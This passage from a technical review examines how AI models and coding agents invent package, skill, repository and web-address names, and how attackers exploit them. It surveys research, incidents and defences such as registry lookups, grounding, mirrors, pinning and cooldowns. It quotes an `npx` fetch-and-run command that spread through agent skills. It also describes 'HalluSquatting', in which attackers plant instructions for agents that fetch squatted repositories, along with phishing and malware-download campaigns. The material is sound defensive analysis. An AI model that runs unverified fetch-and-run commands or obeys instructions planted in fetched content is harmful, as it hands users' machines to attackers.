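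Dates also complicate the measurement, because somebody may have registered a package after the model invented its name. Churilov still counted a name as invented if the package was created after the model's reply. In *Importing Phantoms*, Krishna, Galinkin and colleagues (2025) used an earlier cutoff. They counted a name as invented if the package was registered after the model's training data ended, because the model couldn't have learned about it.

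A live checker could flag packages registered after the model's training cutoff. If a model names such a package from memory, either the match is a coincidence or somebody may have registered the name because models suggest it. The rule would give false alarms for an assistant that searches the web, which can find legitimate packages released last week.

### When somebody registers the invented name

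On October 17, 2025, a collection of 47 model-written skills appeared on GitHub. At least two of them included instructions for agents to run `npx react-codeshift`. The `npx` command downloads a package from npm and runs it in one step. `jscodeshift` and `react-codemod` are real tools, but nobody had published `react-codeshift`. Other people copied the collection, one of them translated it into Japanese, and the command spread to 237 repositories.

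In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, Eriksen (2026), who works for the security company Aikido, describes finding the name while searching GitHub for `npx` commands that called unregistered packages. Eriksen registered it with an empty package on January 14, 2026. An existence check would have rejected the command before that date and accepted it afterwards, and would also have accepted it if an attacker had registered the name first.

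The package had about 74 downloads on the first day, then 4, 1, 3, 1 and 3 over the next five days. Eriksen reports that such packages usually get 60 to 100 downloads on the first day, from security scanners and services that copy the registry, and none after that. Eriksen concludes that the later downloads came from agents following the skills. That is plausible, but download counts don't identify who downloaded the package, and none of the 237 repositories was a major project.

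An earlier demonstration drew far more traffic. In *Diving Deeper into AI Package Hallucinations*, the software developer Willison writes that the researcher Bar Lanyado noticed models repeatedly suggesting `pip install huggingface-cli`, when the correct name is `huggingface[cli]`. Lanyado published a harmless package under the invented name and counted 30,000 downloads in three months. If PyPI is similar to npm, Eriksen's npm figures suggest that scanners and copying services would explain only a small part of those downloads.

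Spracklen and colleagues rejected registry lookups as a defence because an attacker can register an invented package name first. Neither PyPI nor npm reviews a first upload, and anyone with an email address can make one. A lookup still stops names that nobody has registered, and most invented names stay unregistered for months.

Churilov found that 25 of the 2,282 invented names, or roughly 1%, gained a package within about six months. At least one of these packages contained malware, which npm removed. One was empty, and another was a placeholder whose publisher described it as a name reservation. Churilov didn't inspect the contents of the other 22, so they could be attacks, precautions by defenders or ordinary projects that happened to have the same name.

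At least 23 names that the models suggested had hosted malicious packages before the test began. For 13 of them, npm had replaced the malware with a harmless placeholder, so the names still pass an existence check. The other ten were no longer on PyPI. A checker can catch both kinds by also consulting OSV, a public database that includes records of malicious packages, but this won't catch a malicious package that nobody has reported yet.

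Churilov was able to test whether publishing invented names encourages people to register them. On April 30, 2026, a day after sending the list of shared names privately to PyPI and Socket, Churilov accidentally put it in a public repository, where it stayed until November 7. In that time, people registered 1 of the 104 published names and 24 of the 2,178 unpublished ones, about 1% of each group.

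The main comparison matched names by length and by how often models produced them. None of the 87 published names was registered, compared with 2 of the 101 names that exactly four of the five models had invented. The 95% confidence interval for the difference runs from 6.9 percentage points fewer registrations for published names to 2.5 points more, so a doubling of the 1% rate is well within it. Churilov calculates that the study could reliably detect only a rise from 1% to at least about 10.5%. Few people may have seen the list, since the archived copy had only 20 downloads. The result is weak evidence that publication is safe, and the current paper doesn't print any name that an outsider could register.

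### Adding the package's age, releases and maintainers

Besides the package's name, a registry entry usually gives the date of the first upload, the number of releases, an author and a short description. A package registered last month with one release and no author deserves more suspicion than one with ten years of updates, and two groups have developed checks based on this idea.

Hillah and colleagues wrote three rules for packages less than 180 days old. A package triggers a rule if it has only one release, if its author field is empty, or if its description is missing or a single word. Each rule gives a probability that the package is bad, starting from an imaginary record of earlier flags. The empty-author rule starts with 3 correct flags and 7 false alarms, or 30%. After *s* further correct flags and *f* further false alarms, the probability becomes:

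(3 + *s*) / (10 + *s* + *f*)

One false alarm lowers the probability to 27%, and 20 in a row lower it to 10%. The researchers chose the starting numbers by judgement and gave them little weight, so that real cases soon outweigh them. If a package triggers several rules, the checker uses the highest probability. Multiplying the probabilities would wrongly treat the rules as independent, when all three require a new package.

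They tested the rules on 1,734 replies from six models. Two-thirds were the ordinary programming tasks, and the rest answered prompts that asked for obscure or made-up libraries. In the results, precision is the share of flagged replies that really contained an invented name, recall is the share of replies with invented names that the checker flagged, and F1 combines the two:

| | Registry lookup alone | With the metadata rules |
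|---|---|---|
| Replies flagged | 225 | 235 |
| Precision | 95.6% | 91.5% |
| Recall | 88.1% | 88.1% |
| F1 | 0.917 | 0.898 |

The rules added ten flags, all for two packages requested by name in the prompts, `pyzenith` and `chartcraft`. All ten counted as errors because both packages are on PyPI and the answer key treated any registered package as genuine. Neither had a malware record, and the researchers say both may be legitimate young projects.

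Under this answer key, the new rules could therefore only lose points, since a flag would have counted as false even if the package had been malicious. The rules lowered precision by about four points in the experiment, but the results don't show whether they catch attackers. At 30%, the ten flags would be suitable for requesting human review. A system that blocks only above 50% would have let both packages through.

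Raj and Sahu's checker first looks for a 404 from the registry, then passes registered packages to a trained classifier that weighs ten features. Eight come from the name, such as its length, its similarity to a popular package and the presence of words like "super" or "magic". The other two are the number of maintainers and whether the entry links to GitHub. They tested it on 300 handwritten prompts, 105 of them designed to provoke invented names, with Llama 3.1 8B as the main model and Llama 3.3 70B as a backup.

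The checker flagged 179 of 823 package mentions. About half of the flagged names didn't exist, and the other 90 flags fell on registered packages. Many of those 90 may have fallen on working code, because the checker reads names from imports. In Raj and Sahu's own list, `pil`, `faiss`, `tabula`, `haystack`, `camelot` and `skimage` account for 54 of the 90, and each matches what correct code imports from a well-known package. Python programmers import `PIL` from Pillow, for instance. Consulting the import table only after a 404 misses these cases, because registered names don't return a 404. Raj and Sahu instead take the 90 flags as evidence that half of what small models invent already exists on PyPI as squatted names or poor lookalikes, though they didn't inspect each package.

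The classifier was also more elaborate than necessary. The two registry features carried 82% of its weight. A one-line rule that accepted a package with either a listed maintainer or a GitHub link did just as well, with an average F1 of 0.99 against the classifier's 0.98. Requiring both dropped the score to 0.55, because many real packages lack one or the other. The high scores rest on very little data, since each model's test set had 2 to 12 invented names.

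Both features also have practical problems. PyPI's public interface shows maintainers only to a project's administrators, so the maintainer count is often zero for legitimate packages. Anyone can add a GitHub link, and the researchers didn't test what happens when an attacker does. They also expect the checker to misjudge new packages for months, until those packages have links and appear on the list of popular names. Hillah's age limit can misjudge new packages too, because one from a careful developer looks much like one from an attacker. An attacker can also get past the limit by waiting 180 days.

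### What to do with a rejected name

When a package name fails the check, the obvious response is to ask the model again. In Raj and Sahu's test, 186 of the 300 prompts produced acceptable code at the first attempt. Another 28 succeeded on a retry, and 14 more succeeded with a larger backup model. For the remaining 72, the system would warn the user not to install anything. The backup probably did poorly because it came from the same family as the main model and often invented the same names. A model from another company might have done better, but the researchers didn't try one.

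Their system also made the model's choices more random on each retry. That can stop the model from repeating the same mistake, but it may cause new ones, because Spracklen and colleagues found that models invent more packages as randomness increases. Telling the model which name failed and forbidding it to use that name again seems better.

Giving a model real package entries in advance reduces rejections, but the check is still needed. When Djire and colleagues added five registry entries to each prompt, the average share of invented names from their small models fell from 29.7% to 18.1%. But for JavaScript, the share rose in seven of the eight models.

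Spracklen and colleagues thought that a curated list of known good packages would work better than the whole registry, although they called it blunt and warned that it would need constant updating. An invented name appears in the registry as soon as an attacker registers it, but a curated list would still exclude it unless a curator added it by mistake.

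## Letting the model choose only from an approved list

A developer can apply an approved list before or after the model answers. Filtering afterwards is simpler, since the model answers freely and code rejects any name that isn't on the list. But the model may never mention a good answer that is on the list. Suppose a company has approved 400 Python packages, one of which extracts tables from PDFs. A programmer asks the model for such a package, and it names three popular ones that aren't approved. The filter rejects all three, so the programmer gets no recommendation.

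Restricting the choices beforehand avoids this, because the model sees the approved PDF package before it answers. It takes four steps:

1. Somebody builds an index of approved entries. Each entry holds an item's exact identifier, its publisher, a description and the approved version.
2. Software searches the index for entries that match the request and retrieves, say, the ten closest. It usually compares meanings instead of words, using a small model that turns each text into a list of numbers, so that similar texts get similar numbers.
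3. The main model reads the ten descriptions and returns the number of one entry, or "none of these".
4. Code looks up that number and takes the exact identifier and version from the index. It refuses any other reply.

The model never writes the package's name, so it can't misspell or invent one. It can still pick the wrong entry, or pick one when it should decline, as Lee's small models did with permitted values.

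A correct recommendation needs every step to work. Suppose, as a made-up example, that the index holds a suitable entry for 90% of requests, the search finds that entry 80% of the time, and the model then picks it 80% of the time. The user gets the right item in 0.9 × 0.8 × 0.8, or about 58%, of cases. A developer who counted only invented names would find no errors in this system.

The index also has to contain only what somebody has approved. SkillsMP, a catalogue of more than 1.7 million skills, regularly collects them from public GitHub repositories. Yuan and colleagues put a harmless skill on GitHub under a name that the coding agent Claude Code kept inventing. Claude Code recommended the skill again and, when told to install it, found and installed the researchers' copy. An index that automatically collects skills from GitHub could offer the same skill as a valid choice.

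### How often agents invent skill names

The skills study, published in July 2026, is the main evidence on what grounding achieves. Of its 15,000 prompts, 5,000 came from questions on Stack Exchange, Reddit and Hacker News. The other 10,000 each described a popular published skill and asked for its name. Yuan and colleagues tested 12 configurations, made up of four models used directly and eight agents. They counted a name as invented only if they could not find it in the skill registries or on GitHub.

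Between 6.5% and 62.0% of the distinct names from each configuration were invented. The average was 36.0% for the models used directly and 36.9% for the agents. The share of invented names was higher for forum questions than for descriptions, averaging 43.1% compared with 29.4%, partly because many forum questions have no matching skill and the right answer is that none exists.

GPT-5.4-mini had the lowest rate of invented names, but it recommended nothing for 52.5% of the prompts. The same model invented 25.5% of its names inside one agent and 23.3% inside another, so the surrounding software also seems to matter. An agent that rarely answers can still be unreliable when it does. Claude Code recommended nothing for 90.9% of the prompts, and 34.6% of the names it did give were invented.

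Most of these models had little chance to learn real skill names, because Anthropic published the skills standard in December 2025, after their training data ended. Claude Opus 4.7 has more recent training data but still invented 36.7% of its names when it had no search tool. Changing how randomly the models chose their words made little difference. Larger models sometimes did better, but none stopped inventing names.

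### Grounding, self-checking and voting

Yuan and colleagues tested three defences on four open models of 8 to 30 billion parameters, using 2,000 of the prompts. For retrieval grounding, they retrieved the ten closest skills, listed their names in the prompt and told the model to recommend only from that list. For self-refinement, they gave the model its own answer and told it to remove any name it couldn't verify. They also combined the two. The averages were:

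| | Share of names that were invented | Prompts with no recommendation |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 40.8% | 73.9% |
| Retrieval grounding | 3.2% | 68.0% |
| Self-refinement | 33.2% | 87.4% |
| Grounding, then self-refinement | 2.7% | 79.4% |

Grounding didn't eliminate invented names because the models were only instructed to choose from the list, and they didn't always follow the instruction. Granite 3.3 8B still invented 10.0% of its names, while the other three models were all below 2%. Every entry in the index was a real skill, so a line of code checking the model's pick against the ten names would have caught the remaining invented ones.

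Self-refinement mostly made the models recommend fewer names. Ministral-3 8B recommended nothing for 99.3% of the prompts, and 65.0% of the few names it kept were invented, a slightly higher share than before.

A separate yes-or-no test helps explain why. Seven models were asked whether names from their own answers existed, and they rejected 91% of the invented names but accepted only 10.0% of the real ones. Averaging the two rates gives the balanced accuracy of about 51% mentioned earlier, barely above the 50% that a program would score by rejecting every name. The models did little better when judging other models' names, scoring 53%.

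Voting accepts a name only if at least two models produce it. In the study, this removed 92.8% of the invented names but kept only 44.8% of the real ones. Requiring three models removed over 98% of the invented names and kept 21.9% of the real ones. These figures count each name once, however often it was recommended. The 410 invented names that more than one configuration produced made up 15.3% of all invented recommendations, so a two-model vote removes about 85% of those recommendations. The invented names that survive are the most attractive to register, because they reach users of several systems. The votes may not be fully independent, since two of the 12 configurations ran Claude Sonnet 4.6 and three ran GPT-5.4-mini.

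If a catalogue exists, looking the name up is better than voting. By the study's definition, a complete lookup would have rejected every invented name and kept every real one, but it would accept an invented name once somebody registered it.

### Whether grounding made the models less useful

In their abstract, Yuan and colleagues write that grounding "crippled the agent's usefulness". Their results for the individual models don't support this. The table gives each figure before and after grounding. The last column is the share of description prompts for which the model named the right skill:

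| Model | Invented names | No recommendation | Correct skill |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ministral-3 8B | 61.3% → 1.6% | 81.9% → 74.2% | 1.7% → 12.9% |
| Granite 3.3 8B | 46.4% → 10.0% | 70.2% → 63.0% | 2.2% → 15.4% |
| Qwen 3.5 9B | 32.5% → 0.9% | 77.0% → 76.2% | 16.5% → 10.0% |
| Nemotron-Cascade-2 30B | 22.8% → 0.6% | 66.5% → 58.4% | 20.7% → 16.0% |

All four models answered slightly more often with grounding, so they didn't invent fewer names by declining to answer. Correct recommendations rose sharply for the two weaker models and fell for the two stronger ones. The average rose from about 10.3% to 13.6%, a slight improvement for models that were barely useful before. A developer already using Nemotron could reasonably object to grounding, because the model lost nearly a quarter of its correct answers.

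Still, no grounded model named the right skill more than 16.0% of the time. The study doesn't report how often the right skill was among the ten retrieved, so it's unclear which step failed. The search should have been easy, because each of these prompts contained the skill's own description and the index included the descriptions available. The models then saw only the skills' names and had instructions to return nothing unless they were confident. Showing them the descriptions might help a lot. The researchers didn't test grounding on the larger commercial models, which may also choose better.

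### When the user gives only part of the name

Retrieval matters even when the user already knows what they want. A GitHub repository's full name includes its owner, as in `kavishdevar/librepods`, but people tend to ask an assistant to "clone librepods" (download a copy), so the model has to supply the owner.

In *Beware of Agentic Botnets*, Spira, Cohen and colleagues (2026) describe an attack they call HalluSquatting, in which an attacker registers repositories and skills that models tend to invent and plants instructions there for any agent that fetches them. They asked each of six models 100 times for the command to clone each of 15 repositories. The models gave a wrong address 92.4% of the time for ten recent repositories that were trending on GitHub, but 0.9% of the time for five famous ones from 2013 to 2018, probably because those had appeared in their training data.

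In tests of the coding assistant Cursor CLI, 877 of 939 addresses (93.4%) were correct when the assistant searched the web first, compared with 4 of 442 (0.9%) when it didn't. The researchers didn't assign searches at random, so some of the gap could reflect differences between requests. But the gap also appeared within a single model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, which was always right on the recent repositories when it searched and always wrong when it didn't.

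However, assistants often skip the search. Another assistant, Gemini CLI, searched in only about 15% of its runs on the recent repositories. The wording of the request also affected how often models searched. In Cursor CLI, Gemini 3 Flash searched 99% of the time when told to "clone" a repository, but only 2% when asked to print the command for doing so. Claude Sonnet 4.5 searched more often when asked to print the command.

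Search can also find the wrong project. Gemini 3 Flash searched every time it was told to clone `antigravity-manager`, a name that several projects share, and still got the repository's address wrong in 55% of usable replies.

Skills have a similar problem, because the name on a skill's page can differ from the identifier that installs it. On ClawHub, a skill marketplace for the OpenClaw assistant, "DuckDuckGo Web Search" has the identifier `ddg-web-search`, which OpenClaw got wrong in all ten attempts. Across 14 skills and 140 attempts with Claude Sonnet 4.6, OpenClaw produced an unregistered identifier 127 times and the right one 13 times. For three skills with Chinese documentation, the right skill wasn't in the top ten results of an English search. An index that stores both the name and the identifier would fix the mismatch, since code could supply the identifier once the model or user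 had chosen the entry. To fix the search problem, skills need descriptions in the languages that users write in.

Spira and colleagues propose several defences but don't test them as working systems. Developers could change the tool that fetches repositories so that it always searches first, and add examples of correct behaviour to the model's instructions. The tool change is more dependable because it doesn't rely on the model choosing to search. Platforms could stop different owners from using the same repository name, though that would interfere with the common practice of copying a project into one's own account under its original name.

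The researchers also suggest that platforms reserve the names models are likely to invent and redirect each one to the real item. In the skills study, the 500 most repeated invented names accounted for 57% of the invented recommendations from seven configurations. That test ran the same 500 prompts ten times, so coverage would probably be lower for new requests.

The companies disagreed about who is responsible for this problem. GitHub replied that the report described the behaviour of models and agents, not a security flaw in its site. Cline, which makes a coding assistant, said it would consider warnings. ClawHub said it was looking into reserving risky names and requiring a search and a check of the skill's details before a plain-language request can install a skill.

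### Company mirrors and approved tool lists

A company can also enforce an approved list when a machine installs a package, whatever the model recommended. To do this, it can run a curated mirror, a server that supplies only approved packages to the company's machines, so that they don't download from PyPI or npm directly. Some mirrors instead fetch any public package on first request and keep a copy, so they don't enforce a list. If an agent tries to install a package name the model invented from a curated mirror, the command fails, even if an attacker has registered that name on PyPI.

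The mirror works only if the machine has no other route to the public registry. Installers generally let a user specify a different registry, so an agent that writes its own commands could bypass the mirror, perhaps just to get past an error. The company therefore also has to block the public registries on its network.

The mirror must also hold everything an approved package depends on. *Pinning Is Futile* (He, Vasilescu and Kästner, 2025) notes that npm projects commonly have orders of magnitude more indirect dependencies than direct ones. Approving one package can mean approving hundreds, most of which nobody at the company chose.

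An approved tool list limits which tools an agent can call, and the software around the agent refuses any request for a tool that isn't on the list. Each entry should identify both the tool and the server that provides it, because two servers can offer tools with the same name. An entry may also need to limit the tool's arguments, since a tool that reads files can open a password file as easily as a project's documentation.

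### When an approved package changes

On March 31, 2026, an intruder released two malicious versions of axios, a popular JavaScript package for making web requests, after breaking into its lead maintainer's npm account. A sensible list of approved packages could have included axios. Because it was old and popular, with a known maintainer, it would also have passed the metadata checks for new packages. Approving the name `axios` means approving whatever is published next by the maintainer or anyone else with access to the maintainer's account.

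Many projects accept new versions automatically. In npm, `^1.2.0` allows any version from 1.2.0 up to, but not including, 2.0.0, and the installer picks the newest. Pinning replaces the range with an exact version, such as `1.2.0`, so the approval covers only that release.

Pinning by hash also checks the file's contents. A hash is a short string computed from those contents, and in practice any change to the file produces a different string. The reviewer records the hash of the approved file. The installer then computes the hash of the downloaded file and rejects it if the two don't match, which catches a file that somebody has replaced or altered on the way. Hashes are particularly useful for skills that agents download from GitHub, because a repository's owner can move a version label to different code.

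Pinning only the packages that a project names directly can make the project less secure. He et al. simulated a year of npm updates and found that this kind of pinning left projects with more outdated and vulnerable packages. In projects with at least 498 dependencies, it also raised exposure to malicious updates, which they attribute to the way npm resolves dependencies. About 26% of the GitHub repositories in their data were that large.

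A lock file avoids part of this problem by recording the exact version of every package in the project, including the indirect ones. But a library's lock file doesn't apply to the projects that use the library, and regenerating a lock file brings in new versions wherever the project allows a range. An agent that regenerates the file to clear an installation error could replace dozens of approved versions without anyone noticing.

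Even a matching hash shows only that the file is the one somebody reviewed. The skills that Eriksen found on GitHub told agents to run an npm package that didn't exist. Registering that package would not have changed the skills' hashes, but an agent that followed the skills would then have run a stranger's code. Tools on remote servers are harder to verify because the code runs on somebody else's machine and the customer has no file to check. The customer can only record a tool's description and ask for a new review when it changes.

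### Judging a new version by where it came from

When a project updates a package, somebody has to decide whether to trust the new version. pnpm, an alternative installer for npm packages, has an optional rule that refuses a release if the evidence of how it was published is weaker than for an earlier release. Many projects publish through an automated system that leaves a signed record. Someone who steals a maintainer's password and uploads a release by hand may leave no such record, and the rule would then block the release if an earlier one had a record.

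*A Difference Without a Distinction* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) reconstructed 12 attacks that used stolen credentials, involving 41 malicious releases of 15 packages. The rule would have flagged 17 of the 41. It can't flag releases from projects that never published signed records, and in a wider count of npm attacks, only 17.5% of the packages had earlier evidence of this kind. Attackers could also have gotten 15 of the 17 flagged releases past the rule by adding evidence of their own.

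The rule blocked the latest version of 16 of the 1,000 most popular npm packages. Fourteen of the 16 were blocked because of one release, version 6.3.1 of `semver`, which many other packages depend on. That release was a genuine security fix that a maintainer had published by hand for users of an older version.

### Waiting before installing a new release

A waiting period, often called a cooldown, blocks a release until it reaches a certain age, in the hope that somebody else will discover first if it is malicious. Early versions had a different purpose. According to *package managers need to cool down* (2026), the update service Depfu introduced one in 2019 to reduce the number of updates developers had to handle. Willison lists seven packaging tools that added or extended waiting periods between September 2025 and February 2026, including pip, pnpm and npm.

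Many attacks on popular packages are short. In September 2025, an attacker published malicious versions of chalk, debug and about a dozen other packages, which together had more than 2 billion downloads a week. npm removed them after roughly two hours, according to GitHub's *The case for a cooldown*. In Santos-Grueiro's reconstructions, the median malicious release stayed online for 3.1 hours. A strict one-day wait would have kept out 36 of the 41 releases. A three-day wait would have kept out 40, as many as a seven-day wait, because none of those 40 stayed online for more than 2.5 days. The removal time of the remaining release is unknown.

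The sample includes only attacks that somebody noticed and wrote up, so it probably favours short ones. GitHub acknowledges that waiting does little against hidden code that stays dormant or a maintainer who turns hostile. Waiting also relies on other people and automated scanners to examine the release in the meantime, which is more likely for chalk than for an obscure skill.

Default waiting periods vary between tools. Since July 2026, Dependabot, GitHub's automatic update service, has waited three days before proposing a new version (GitHub, *Dependabot version updates introduce default package cooldown*, 2026). Before that, *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects* (Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues, 2026) found that 135 of 1,462 popular repositories had chosen to set a waiting period, most often seven days. JFrog's support page *Recently published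 NPM packages may be blocked for 24 hours* lists a one-day default for recent versions of pnpm and Yarn, and none for npm.

pnpm's default has an exception that matters for invented names. pnpm's *Mitigating supply chain attacks* describes the wait as holding back any newly published package for a day. But Santos-Grueiro explains that, by default, pnpm accepts a younger release when no matching version is old enough. If somebody registered an invented name an hour ago, every version of that package is too young, so the default wouldn't block it. In recent versions, setting the wait explicitly makes it strict. Even a strict wait, like Hillah's age limit, fails against an attacker who lets the package age first.

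### When the new release is an urgent fix

A waiting period delays good releases as well as bad ones. In December 2025, attackers started exploiting a serious flaw in React, a popular library for building web interfaces, within hours of its disclosure. Cloudflare's *React2Shell and related RSC vulnerabilities threat brief* describes them scanning the internet for vulnerable sites. Waiting a day for the fix would have left a site open to attack for another day. *How pnpm's minimumReleaseAgeExclude Helped with Emergency Security Updates* (Shigeoka, 2025) gives React as an example of a library that needed an urgent update while a team's 24-hour wait blocked it. The team added an exemption to get the fix.

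Socket's *npm introduces minimumreleaseage and bulk oidc configuration* notes that the first version of npm's waiting period for new releases had no built-in way to exempt a package. AWS's instructions for its own version of Linux combine a one-day wait for npm with scripts that can override waiting periods for known defects. Dependabot proposes security updates immediately, and GitHub says critical fixes are therefore "never delayed".

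That holds only for fixes labelled as security updates. Maintainers often release a fix before they disclose the flaw, to avoid alerting attackers. *A Fine-Grained Empirical Study of Upstream Security Events and Downstream Mitigation* (2026) counted 332 fixes in Maven, a system for distributing Java packages, that maintainers had released without saying that they repaired a vulnerability. For 271 of them, the fixed version came out before the flaw appeared in the main US vulnerability database. Until the flaw is listed there, an automatic exemption cannot identify the release as urgent.

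A delay of a few days may not matter much to a project that updates slowly. In the same study, projects without Dependabot took a median of 110.6 days to adopt a fixed release. The delay matters more for a team that normally installs fixes the same day, particularly if its software is exposed to the internet.

An exemption should name an exact version. Santos-Grueiro found 290 public repositories that exempted whole packages from pnpm's weaker-evidence rule. That rule blocked a genuine axios release, 0.30.3, because the maintainers had published it by hand. Exempting axios by name, rather than only 0.30.3, would also have let in the attacker's release, 0.30.4.

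## Checking web addresses, shops and contact details before showing them

The web has no equivalent of a package registry for organisations. The domain name system (DNS) connects a name such as `example.com` to a server, but it doesn't record whether the server's owner is the bank, shop or airline the user asked about. Developers therefore have to combine several checks, most of them weak.

### Four checks on one address

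Suppose an employee of a made-up company, Norvane Logistics, asks an assistant where to log in to the staff benefits portal. The real portal is a page on the company's site, `norvane.example`. The model answers `norvane-benefits.example`, which nobody has registered. (Real sites don't end in `.example`, which stands in here for `.com`.)

The easiest check is a DNS lookup, which shows whether the domain resolves (leads to a server). It rejects the invented portal as long as nobody owns the name. It can also reject a correct address, because some companies run staff portals that resolve only inside their own networks. DNS covers only domains, so the software has to request the page itself to catch an invented page on a real site. Some sites block automated requests, which can make a real page look missing.

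A domain's registration record usually shows when it was registered. A developer might use this date to reject domains less than 90 days old, for example. A reputation service keeps verdicts on domains that people have reported or scanners have examined. A verdict of "malicious" is a strong reason to remove a link, but "unknown" may mean only that nobody has checked the domain yet.

An independently kept directory shows which organisation a domain belongs to. In the United States, for example, only public bodies can register a `.gov` domain, and the FDIC, which insures bank deposits, publishes the web addresses of the banks it covers. For Norvane, the directory could be a list of portals that the company's IT department maintains. The directory mustn't come from web pages that the model reads, or a stranger could add an entry by publishing a page.

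The four checks give these results for the invented portal:

| | Before anyone registers it | An hour after a stranger does | A year later |
|---|---|---|---|
| Does it resolve? | No, reject | Yes, accept | Yes, accept |
| Is it old enough? | No record, reject | No, reject | Yes, accept |
| Does a reputation service know it? | Unknown | Unknown | Malicious if somebody has reported it |
| Does a directory list it for Norvane? | No, reject | No, reject | No, reject |

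Only the directory gives the right answer in every column. The comparison has to be exact, because a check that only searches for the company's domain somewhere in the address would accept `norvane.example.portal-login.example`, which belongs to whoever owns `portal-login.example`. It's safer to discard the model's address and show the one in the directory. In 2025, Nicole Carignan of the security company Darktrace gave Security Magazine similar advice, recommending that site names generated by models be replaced with names from a real source.

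(None of these checks looks for private data that an agent might leak inside an address, which is a separate problem.)

### How often models invent addresses

Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams* (2025) describes an early test in which the security company asked a model ordinary questions about where to log in to 50 brands' sites. The model gave 131 site names, 34% of which the brands didn't control. Nearly 30% of the total were unregistered, inactive or parked (holding only a placeholder), and another 5% belonged to unrelated businesses. SC Media identifies the model as OpenAI's GPT-4.1, which is now old. A DNS lookup would have caught the unregistered names but not the unrelated businesses, which checks on domain age and reputation would probably have missed too.

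Unit 42's *Phantom Squatting*, published on June 30, 2026, describes a far larger test. Unit 42 is the research group of Palo Alto Networks, a security company. Its software researched the products and portals of 913 brands, then sent 685,339 queries about them to two models at three levels of randomness. The replies contained 2.1 million different addresses, which the researchers looked up:

| Result | Addresses | Share |
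|---|---|---|
| Didn't resolve | 809,455 | 37.28% |
| High risk, such as parked domains or pages with too little content to judge | 41,313 | 1.90% |
| Already flagged as malicious | 13,229 | 0.61% |

The addresses that didn't resolve contained about 250,000 domains that anyone could register, according to Unit 42. It classes only 10.8% of these addresses, or about 87,630, as wholly invented domains, and the rest as invented pages or subdomains of existing ones. (A subdomain adds a prefix, such as `admin.`, to a domain.) But 87,630 addresses can't contain 250,000 different domains, so many of the domains Unit 42 classed as existing must have been unregistered too.

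Ordinary users would probably see much lower rates. Unit 42 wrote the queries to exploit known weaknesses, such as models' tendency to accept a false premise. One query asked for the administrative dashboard of a postal marketplace's campaigns, which few customers would need. The researchers also discarded replies that gave no address or said it was unknown. Both models were small, cheap versions from April and June 2025. For one model, 44.6% of addresses failed to resolve, compared with 27.5% for the other. Palo Alto Networks sells URL filtering, which the article recommends.

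The study counted 13,229 addresses as malicious because threat-intelligence systems had already flagged them. A lookup in the same systems would have removed every one, but this doesn't show how well reputation checks work, because the study can't be used to estimate how many bad addresses those systems missed.

### Why new domains pass reputation filters

A domain is added to a blocklist after somebody reports it, and to a threat feed after somebody sees it used in an attack. A reputation score needs weeks or months of traffic. A domain registered this morning has no reports, sightings or traffic history, so it gets through, as unknown items do with any denylist.

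Attackers can finish their work before a domain's record shows that it is malicious. On March 8, 2026, Unit 42's two models produced 13 addresses on an unregistered domain that resembled a national postal service's marketplace. On March 31, somebody registered the domain and put a phishing kit there, a ready-made fake site for collecting payment details. The attacker had the kit on a server before registering the name. In another case, a page offering a fake postal app appeared 51 days after the models first produced its domain. Attackers can also keep a domain's record clean for longer by showing scanners a harmless page or putting a CAPTCHA in front of the malicious one.

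Unit 42 keeps a watchlist of unregistered domains that models invent. It monitors new registrations and inspects any domain on the list as soon as somebody buys it. It also compares the domain's registrar, organisation and servers with those of the brand's known domains, to avoid flagging domains the brand bought itself. The watchlist is in effect a denylist prepared in advance, so it covers only the names that Unit 42's own queries produced.

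The evidence that attackers' domain names match ones models invent is stronger than the evidence that attackers are exploiting those inventions, though the article presents these cases as proof of exploitation. A brand's name followed by "login" is an obvious choice for any phisher, and Unit 42 doesn't describe a victim who reached one of these sites through a model's answer. An attacker registered one domain, which imitated a bank in the United Arab Emirates, 11 months before Unit 42's models produced it. The overlap still helps defenders, whether or not the attackers asked a model.

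The bank's imitator also shows the limits of checking a domain's age, since an 11-month-old domain would pass most age rules. A higher minimum age would reject many more good sites. According to a summary quoted by Willison, a report by the research firm Interisle counted 85 million new registrations in 2025 under generic endings such as `.com`. Blocklists included 8.5 million of them, or 10%, and the true share of abusive domains may be nearer 20%. Even at 20%, a rule that refused every new domain would refuse four non-abusive domains for each abusive one. The ratio may be quite different among the new domains that models recommend, but nobody seems to have measured it.

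### When the model repeats what somebody planted

In all these cases the model made up the address. A model can also accurately report what it read on a web page that was planted to mislead. Retrieval grounding reduces invention but doesn't prevent this, because the search can find the planted page. An existence check doesn't help either, because the page exists.

Netcraft saw an early example in 2025, when Perplexity, a search engine that answers with a language model, gave a phishing page as its first source for the Wells Fargo login page. On May 26, 2026, Microsoft (2026) described a larger campaign that used fake download sites for popular PC utilities such as HWMonitor and CrystalDiskInfo. The attackers wanted to mine cryptocurrency on computers with powerful graphics cards. Microsoft had identified more than 150 malicious domains since March.

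Most of Microsoft's account concerns manipulated results in ordinary search engines. The evidence about chatbots is more tentative. In April, Microsoft saw reports that users "may have been directed" to the sites by chatbots, and traffic data in which chatbots appeared as a possible source. It also published one chatbot answer that linked to the sites, but said the example didn't indicate a systemic problem with any particular AI service.

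The campaign would have defeated several simple checks. The download contained a genuine copy of the utility alongside a malicious file, so the program would have worked when a user opened it. The files came from subdomains of `gleeze.com`, which Microsoft links to a company that lets customers create their own subdomains on its domains. A check on the age of `gleeze.com` would have returned the age of that company's domain, not the attacker's subdomain. A short list of the official download pages for common utilities would have worked better.

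Microsoft also recommends a Windows rule that can block programs from running unless they are widespread enough, old enough or on a trusted list. This protects a user who has already followed a bad link, but it also blocks some new or obscure programs that are harmless.

Some planted sites are already known to be bad. ESET, another security vendor, told Inside Retail in September 2026 that ChatGPT's search results had sent people to fake shops, imitation login pages and other sites already identified as unsafe. A reputation lookup just before display can easily catch these sites if the lookup service has them on record.

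### Why phone numbers are so hard to check

Scammers have planted fake customer-service numbers in search results for years. Gizmodo describes a report by the security company Aurascape that found such numbers in answers from Perplexity and in Google's AI Overviews, the summaries above its search results. Later, in September 2026, Vigilance Security reported a campaign it calls Dark Sourcery, which planted fake contact details for at least 374 companies, including airlines, banks and travel sites. IlSoftware.it's *Dark Sourcery colpisce 374 aziende manipolando le risposte dei chatbot* notes that 374 is the firm's own count, not an independent one.

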